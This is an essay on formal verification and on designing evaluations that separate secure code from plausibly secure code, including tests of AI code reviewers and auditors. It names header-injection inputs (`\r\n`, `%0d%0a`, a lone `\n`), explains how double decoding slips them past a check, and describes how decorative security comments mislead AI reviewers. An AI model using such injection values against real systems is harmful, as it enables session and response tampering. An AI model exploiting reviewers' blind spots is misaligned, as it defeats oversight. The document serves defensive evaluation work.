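In October 2026, Anthropic and the company Theorem applied formal proof to much more code. According to Anthropic's *LLMs are making formal software verification feasible at a much larger scale* (2026), Claude proved security properties of the compiled code of 123 open-source libraries and found bugs that had gone unnoticed for years. Because the proofs are about compiled code, they don't rely on the compiler being correct. Smith's *Claude Writes 180 Million Lines of Proofs* (2026) reports that they run to 180 million lines.

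EconoTimes' *Anthropic Details Claude's No-Crash Proofs for 239 Fuzz-Test Entry Points* (2026) describes proofs for 239 functions that Google's OSS-Fuzz project uses for fuzzing. The proofs establish that the program exits normally, without a crash, a memory error or a failed assertion. They apply only to inputs under 64 MB and to a mathematical model of a RISC-V processor running Linux.

This is a far better specification than `result >= 0`. Memory errors are among the most dangerous faults in C code, and within those limits the proofs rule them out for every input, which fuzzing cannot do. But many attacks don't involve memory errors. A C version of `set_language` could be proved free of them and still let an attacker add a cookie to the response, because writing a line break into a header breaks no memory rule.

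### From the code to the specification

A small program can check 180 million lines of proof, so nobody needs to read them. But the check can also rely on other software, such as a compiler. Trail of Bits' *A “proof” of Fermat’s Last Theorem that fits the margin* (2026) describes a bug that let Lean appear to accept a very short proof of that theorem. For one unusual input, Lean's logical definition of a text operation gave an empty string while its compiled version gave a non-empty one, and any statement can be proved from such a contradiction. The bug affects only proofs that rely on Lean's compiler, and a single command lists what a proof assumes. Lean's developers fixed the bug within five days.

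People still have to read the specification and the assumptions. Tolmach and Klaus (2026), in *The proof is in the spec*, argue that deciding what to prove has become the bottleneck as AI makes proofs easier to produce. They work for a company that sells verification, but the examples from IronFleet and libcrux support their argument. A specification is usually much shorter than the program and doesn't change each time somebody rewrites the code, so an expert can spend longer on each line.

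A missing requirement is still hard to notice. If Cloudflare's author had put the rule about redirect addresses into a specification, the proof would have failed until the code enforced it, but if he had forgotten the rule there too, the proof would have succeeded and the attack would still have worked. A team can look for such gaps as Silva and colleagues did, by giving the proof tool a program that it should reject. For the header function, that could be the version with only a type check. If the tool accepts that version, the specification is missing a requirement.

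## An evaluation that separates secure code from plausible code

A header function with only a type check can reveal a careless reviewer, a weak set of attacks or a gap in a specification. The evaluation below builds on such programs. It combines methods from published studies, but nobody has run it as a whole. The reviewers, auditors and counts in the worked examples are invented.

### Four groups of programs

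The evaluator collects 100 short programs with one known vulnerability each, along with a repaired version of each program. The evaluator then copies all 200 and adds signs of security to the copies that don't affect the attack, such as a comment, a log entry or a useless check. For the header function, the four versions are:

| | Plain | Decorated |
|---|---|---|
| Flawed | Assigns the value unchanged | Also has the type check and the comment about security |
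| Secure | Rejects line breaks | Also has the same type check and comment |

Moon and colleagues used this layout for contest programs, with decorated copies of both correct and incorrect solutions. In a security evaluation, a decoration might accidentally stop the attack or break the program, so the evaluator runs the functional tests and the planned attack on all four versions and drops the set if the decoration changes a result.

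Reviewers aren't told which group a program belongs to. Each reviewer sees only one of a program's four versions, because someone who saw both the plain and decorated copies would notice that only the decoration differs. An AI reviewer gets a new session for every program.

Suppose the reviewers flag these programs as vulnerable:

| | Flawed | Secure | Difference |
|---|---|---|---|
| Plain | 70 of 100 | 20 of 100 | 50 points |
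| Decorated | 40 of 100 | 10 of 100 | 30 points |

The difference measures how well the reviewers distinguish flawed code from secure code. It would be zero for a reviewer who flagged everything. Decoration lowers the difference from 50 points to 30 and causes the reviewers to miss 30 flaws they would otherwise have flagged.

Some of this loss comes from leniency, because the decoration also halved the false alarms. The share due to leniency can be estimated from the odds of a flag, which for plain programs are 70 to 30 if the program is flawed and 20 to 80 if it is secure, a ratio of 9.3. If decoration had made the reviewers more lenient without changing this ratio, they would have flagged about 51 decorated flawed programs along with the 10 secure ones. They flagged only 40, so on this model leniency accounts for about 19 of the 30 hidden flaws and worse discrimination for the other 11.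 Telling reviewers to be stricter could recover the 19 but not the 11, and it would cause more false alarms.

A hundred programs per group is barely enough to distinguish the 20-point fall in discrimination from no change. If the groups are treated as independent samples, the 95% interval for the fall runs from about 4 to 36 points.

### What counts as a flag

The evaluator has to decide what counts as a flag before the reviews begin. *What Moves the Ceiling on Automated Audit* (Dong, 2026) tested AI auditors on programs with hidden functional faults. When only objections serious enough to block the program counted, one model caught 26 percentage points fewer faulty programs than another over eight readings. When any objection counted, the same model caught about 25 points more than the other.

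The instructions also have to be the same for all four groups. In a test on scientific code, Dong reworded the task to focus on the one step under review. The share of correct programs flagged fell from 68.7% to 36.0%, and the share of faulty programs flagged fell from 87.7% to 72.8%, although the programs hadn't changed.

A reviewer can flag a flawed program for the wrong reason, so the evaluator should also record whether the reviewer identified the actual vulnerability. Liu and Böhme used a language model from a different family than the ones under test to match reports to known vulnerabilities, and people confirmed the matches. They used only vulnerabilities disclosed after the tested model's training data ended, so the model was unlikely to have memorised them.

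The "secure" programs may contain flaws that the evaluator doesn't know about. Dong read every flag on supposedly clean reports and datasets and found that some described real defects introduced by accident during construction. An evaluator who doesn't read the flags may count a reviewer's best findings as false alarms.

### Deleting a defence

The evaluator knows which defences in the four groups are decorative because the evaluator added them, but nobody knows this about code a model has just written. A removal test can help. Its procedure comes from *mutation testing*, in which programmers deliberately damage a program to see whether its tests fail.

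*Will My Tests Tell Me If I Break This Code?* (2016) describes an extreme form of mutation testing, which deletes everything a function does and reruns the tests that use it. If they all still pass, they weren't checking what the function does. *Extreme mutation testing in practice* (2021) cites an analysis of 19 open-source projects in which the median share of functions whose tests all still passed was 10.1%.

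Mutation testing judges the tests, whereas the removal test judges the defence. The evaluator runs the attacks, deletes one defence and runs them again. If no outcome changes, the defence did nothing against those attacks. Here are the results for a header function with both the type check and the line-break check:

| Version | Attack with `\r\n` |
|---|---|
| Complete | Fails |
| Without the type check | Fails |
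| Without the line-break check | Succeeds |

The type check did nothing against this attack.

If removing a defence doesn't change the test results, the defence may be useless, or the tests may not include the attacks it stops. Hill (2026), in *Four Ways to Forge a Bundle My Own Verifier Calls Clean*, examined a program that checks published results against their supporting files. Hill deleted, one at a time, each of the 112 statements the program uses to reject bad input. For 75 of them, every test still passed. A collection of 16 tampered files, made to prove that the program could reject forgeries, exposed only 10 of the deletions. Yet most of the statements did have an effect, because after Hill wrote tests aimed at individual statements, the tests exposed 112 of 119 deletions in a slightly larger version of the program. Before calling a defence theater, an evaluator therefore needs to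 test it with attacks it is supposed to stop.

The evaluator can check the attacks by deliberately weakening secure programs and seeing whether the attacks detect the changes, a method *Mutation Analysis for Security* (2013) proposed for judging penetration tests. *HardSecBench* (2026), a benchmark for hardware-related code, keeps a task only if its tests detect at least half of the damaged versions, and the tests for the tasks it keeps detect 70.2% on average. Some of the undetected changes may be harmless, but an attack set with this score could easily make a working defence look useless.

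When deleting a defence, the evaluator should make an escaping function return its input unchanged and a validation function accept everything. An escaping function that returned an empty string would still stop the attack. The program also has to keep running. *A Comprehensive Study of Pseudo-tested Methods* (2018) describes a function in the Java library jsoup for which the tests caught all 69 small changes, because each change crashed the program. The same tests all passed when the researchers deleted the function's entire body. A crash after a deletion is likewise weak evidence about the defence, so the evaluator should look for an attack that used to fail and now succeeds.

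The oracle must be able to detect when an attack succeeds. In one of Farinha's tests, a function that calculates Fibonacci numbers received an enormous input. A version with an upper limit rejected the input and finished the test in 190 milliseconds, while a version without the limit kept calculating until the test system stopped it after 60 seconds. The AI judge passed both, so a removal test using this judge would have wrongly concluded that the limit gave no protection. In two other tasks, the judge passed every security test on code that had never run. An oracle that measures an effect, such as a second header or a missed time limit, avoids both mistakes.

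### Defences that overlap

Suppose the header function and the web framework both reject line breaks. If an evaluator deletes either check, the other still stops the attack. An evaluator who deletes only one check at a time would therefore call both security theater, although either is enough by itself. Deleting both lets the attack through, which reveals the mistake.

Testing every combination of defences soon becomes impractical. Five defences can be present or absent in 32 combinations, and 20 defences in more than a million. A procedure that needs fewer versions is to delete each defence individually from the complete program, then delete all of them and restore each one individually. For five defences, this takes 12 versions, including the complete program and the one with no defences.

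The procedure needs both tests, restoring each defence alone and deleting each from the complete program, because some defences work only together. Suppose the program decodes a value and then rejects line breaks, and the server later decodes the value again. If an attacker sends the line break as `%0d%0a`, the check catches it only after the first decoding. Restoring either step alone won't stop the attack, but deleting either from the complete program lets it through. The procedure can still miss larger combinations, so pairs of defences that handle the same value are also worth testing.

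If the attack still fails after every deletion, something outside the program may be stopping it, or the attack may be broken. Running the attack in the same environment on a version known to be vulnerable helps to tell which.

A duplicate defence still protects the program if somebody later breaks the other one, so it isn't theater. Some defences slow an attacker down or limit the damage without stopping the attack. For a limit on login attempts, for example, the evaluator should compare how many guesses an attacker gets per hour with and without it. A defence that fails the removal test may still be worth keeping for another purpose, as the type check is.

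### Hidden attacks on finished code

To count as secure, a program has to pass the functional tests and withstand attacks its author has never seen. The author, whether a person or a model, hands in the finished code, and the evaluator stores a hash of it so that any later change can be detected. A separate team writes the attacks only after that, so the author can't block a few known attack strings and leave the underlying vulnerability in place.

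The attackers may read the code and adapt to it, as real attackers can with open-source software. To keep the comparison fair, the evaluator then runs every attack on every program written for the same task. Each attack must also succeed against a flawed reference solution and fail against a secure one, as in CWEval.

Faulty tests can make a secure program score badly. Some of the functional tests that Farinha used sent card numbers with invalid check digits, so an application that verified card numbers failed. In two BaxBench scenarios, the security tests end without a result by design, and no program can count as secure. When reporting results, the evaluator should therefore separate programs that couldn't be assessed from those that withstood the attacks. Otherwise, an application that refuses the test's input would be rewarded for refusing it if counted as secure, or penalized for strict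 validation if counted as vulnerable.

It also matters whether the model knows the owner's rules. Farinha gave a coding agent written security requirements for 59 Python tasks, and the share of programs that passed every security test rose from 44.1% to 78.0%, but the share that passed every functional test fell from 42.4% to 33.9%. The requirements came from Farinha's own manual and an AI judge scored the tests, so the exact gain is uncertain. Still, a model that never sees the rules has to guess them as well as implement them. Running the evaluation both with and without the rules would help separate the two problems.

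### Planted vulnerabilities

Nobody knows how many vulnerabilities a real program contains, so an evaluator can't directly calculate the share that an audit missed. The evaluator can get around this by planting known vulnerabilities. In *Quantitative Evaluation of Capture-Recapture Models to Control Software Inspections*, Briand, El Emam and colleagues trace the idea to a 1972 report by Mills.

Suppose the evaluator plants 20 vulnerabilities, and the auditors find 15 of them along with 12 genuine ones. If genuine vulnerabilities are as easy to find as planted ones, the auditors found about three quarters of the genuine ones, so the program had about 16 and about 4 remain undiscovered. This estimate is rough, because finding 15 out of 20 is compatible with a true detection rate from about 51% to 91%.

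The larger problem is making the planted vulnerabilities realistic. Briand and colleagues mention Musa's objection that planted defects are much easier to find than natural ones. If so, the auditors look better than they are, and the estimate of remaining vulnerabilities is too low. *Beyond Rule-Based Mutation Testing* (2026) describes a way to make subtler faults. A language model adds a bug to a correct program, and the bug qualifies only if the program still passes its visible tests but fails a hidden one. For a security audit, the altered program should pass all its functional tests but be vulnerable to one attack.

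Planting many vulnerabilities close together distorts the result. In *Beyond Single Bugs* (2025), the model Qwen2.5-72B found 91% of the vulnerabilities in C files that contained one, 55% in files with three and 44% in files with five. *MultiVulnBench*, by Gupta, Pushkar and colleagues, reports the same tendency on a benchmark of 20,000 files. An evaluator who put all 20 vulnerabilities into one file would probably overestimate how much an AI auditor misses in ordinary code. Spreading them over separate copies of the program avoids this.

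Each planted vulnerability should also break a rule that the auditors know. In Dong's main test, models from three families failed to flag 57 of the 110 faulty programs on any reading. Two AI raters judged that the task descriptions for 44 of these left unclear what the program should do. Auditors have the same difficulty detecting violations of an access rule they haven't been told.

### Estimating what nobody found

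The evaluator can also estimate how many vulnerabilities both auditors missed from the overlap between their lists, as with two AI reviewers. The method is called *capture-recapture* because ecologists use it to estimate how many fish are in a lake by catching and marking some, then counting the marked fish in a second catch.

Suppose one auditor finds 12 vulnerabilities, another finds 10, and 6 are on both lists. With *n*₁ and *n*₂ findings and *m* in common, the estimated total is:

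*N* = *n*₁ × *n*₂ / *m* = 12 × 10 / 6 = 20

Together the auditors know of 12 + 10 − 6 = 16 vulnerabilities, so an estimated 4 remain. Chapman's correction for small samples gives nearly the same total:

(*n*₁ + 1)(*n*₂ + 1) / (*m* + 1) − 1 = 13 × 11 / 7 − 1 ≈ 19.4

The usual 95% interval around this figure extends to about 25, so the auditors might have found every vulnerability or missed nine, even if all the method's assumptions hold.

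They rarely do, because auditors share blind spots. Suppose the program has another 10 vulnerabilities in its access rules, which neither auditor examined. The two lists and the estimate of 20 stay the same, but the true total is 30, so 14 vulnerabilities remain undiscovered instead of 4.

The estimate can be too low even if the auditors work independently and examine everything. If each auditor has a 90% chance of finding each of 10 easy vulnerabilities and a 15% chance of finding each of 20 hard ones, each finds 9 easy and 3 hard ones on average. Their findings overlap on about 8.1 easy and 0.45 hard ones, so the formula gives 12 × 12 / 8.55, or about 17, when the true total is 30. Most of the overlap comes from the easy vulnerabilities, which makes both auditors look more thorough than they are.

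*Estimating the agent actions that no log recorded* (Theodoro, 2026) shows how badly shared failures can distort the method's estimates. The study estimated how many AI agent actions were missing from logs in a test system where the true number was known. With two logs that lost data in the same outages, the 95% interval contained the true number in only 10 of 277 runs. With a third record of a different kind, the final state of the system, a related estimate succeeded in 269 of the 277. Theodoro warns that such an estimate can fail with no sign of it in the output, so one has to examine how the records were made.

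Two runs of the same AI model are a poor substitute for two auditors. *Snyk VulnBench JS 1.0* (2026) reports five repeated scans with each of several models. Of 158 findings that matched those of Snyk's own scanner, 134 appeared in all five scans. Two such scans would overlap so much that the estimate of undiscovered vulnerabilities would be close to zero. Cloudflare gives a similar reason for not relying on one model to scan its code.

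Using models from different companies helps, but they also miss some of the same faults. Six model families missed 32 of Dong's 110 faulty programs in all 40 readings. A reader and somebody who attacks the running program should produce more independent lists. Finifter and Wagner's readers found 71 vulnerabilities and their attack tool found 39, with 19 in common. The formula gives an estimated total of about 146, of which they had found 91. This estimate may be too high, because readers and attack tools are good at finding different kinds of vulnerabilities, which makes the overlap unusually small.

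The lists need cleaning before anyone compares them. *An Analysis of How Many Undiscovered Vulnerabilities Remain in Information Systems* (2023) rejects capture-recapture for crashes found by fuzzing, partly because it's hard to tell whether two crashes have the same cause. Counting one vulnerability as two shrinks the overlap and raises the estimate. False alarms that appear on only one list also raise the estimate.

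Two auditors are also too few. Briand and colleagues tested several versions of the method on inspections in which NASA software professionals reviewed requirements documents with known defects. With fewer than four inspectors, none of the versions was accurate enough, and most estimates were too low. With four or five, the better versions had a typical error of 5% to 16%. Those versions allow for some defects being harder to find than others, but they can't count defects that no inspector could find, so a low estimate is weak evidence that few defects remain.

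### Sixty attacks that fail

Suppose the evaluator generates 60 random attacks of one kind and none succeeds. If each attack had a probability *p* of succeeding, independently of the others, the chance that all 60 would fail is (1 − *p*)⁶⁰. Setting this to 5% gives the largest success rate that is still reasonably compatible with the result:

*p* = 1 − 0.05^(1/60) ≈ 0.049

So the evaluator can say with 95% confidence that fewer than about 5% of such attacks succeed. This upper bound is approximately 3/*n*, where *n* is the number of failed attacks. To lower the bound to one in a thousand, the evaluator would need about 3,000 failed attacks.

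Even for random attacks, 5% isn't reassuring. Someone who can try 100 times, with a 4.9% chance each time, has a better than 99% chance of getting in at least once.

The bound also applies only to attacks from the same generator. If all 60 attacks insert the pair `\r\n` at random places in a header value, their failure does not bound the success rate of an attacker who reads the code and sends a lone `\n`.

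*STADS* (2018) applies similar reasoning to fuzzing and estimates the chance that the next input will make the program do something new. In one example, the chance after 100 hours was about 2 in 100 million, so the next discovery would take about 50 million more inputs on average. This estimate can help a tester decide when to stop that fuzzer, but it doesn't describe what a person or another fuzzer would find.

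*LLMs + Security = Trouble* points out that when tests find no vulnerability, it is often only because they didn't reach it. The defender's test attacks have to be safe, repeatable and within budget, while a real attacker can spend months on a single target and learn from every crash, log entry or delay.

The evaluation should therefore include a stage in which skilled people and AI agents choose each attack based on how the last one went. If they fail, the evaluator cannot honestly express that failure as a percentage and can only report who tried, with what access and for how long.

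### Cost, realism and who should run it

The largest expense is people's time. Judging each of the 400 programs in the four groups once takes 100 hours at 15 minutes per program. Attacks have become much cheaper to produce. With von Arx and colleagues' system, 40 scenarios cost less than $160 to produce and would take about 10 hours to check by hand. Some of the work will be wasted, since *HardSecBench* had to discard 246 of its 1,170 candidate tasks.

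Few organisations need the whole design. A company choosing an AI reviewer needs the four groups to see how decoration affects the reviewer's verdicts. A company about to release a login server would learn more from hidden attacks and removal tests on that server. If the server protects something valuable, the company should then add an audit with planted vulnerabilities, which belong in a separate copy that never goes online.

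Half of the programs in the four groups are flawed, which makes flags look more reliable than they would be in everyday work. In the decorated groups, 40 of the 50 flags are correct. If only 50 of 1,000 decorated programs were flawed, reviewers with the same flag rates would flag 20 flawed programs and 95 secure ones, so only about 17% of their flags would be correct. Reviewers who expect few flaws may also read less carefully than participants in an experiment. An evaluator could reduce this problem by mixing the test programs into a reviewer's normal work, with the reviewer's consent but without revealing when they will appear.

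The decorations should come from real model output where possible, because a comment written by the evaluator might be too crude for anyone to believe. A type check copied from a generated header program, for example, has already appeared in code that somebody might have used.

The company that wrote the code shouldn't run the evaluation, and neither should a firm that sells one of the tools under test. Both can influence the result without cheating, by choosing familiar weaknesses. A customer, a regulator or a non-profit testing group would have less reason to favour a particular outcome. One group should plant the vulnerabilities, another should look for them and a third should write the hidden attacks. The evaluator should publish the scoring rules before the work begins. It can publish the programs and attacks afterwards so that others can check the results, but the next evaluation will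 then need new ones.
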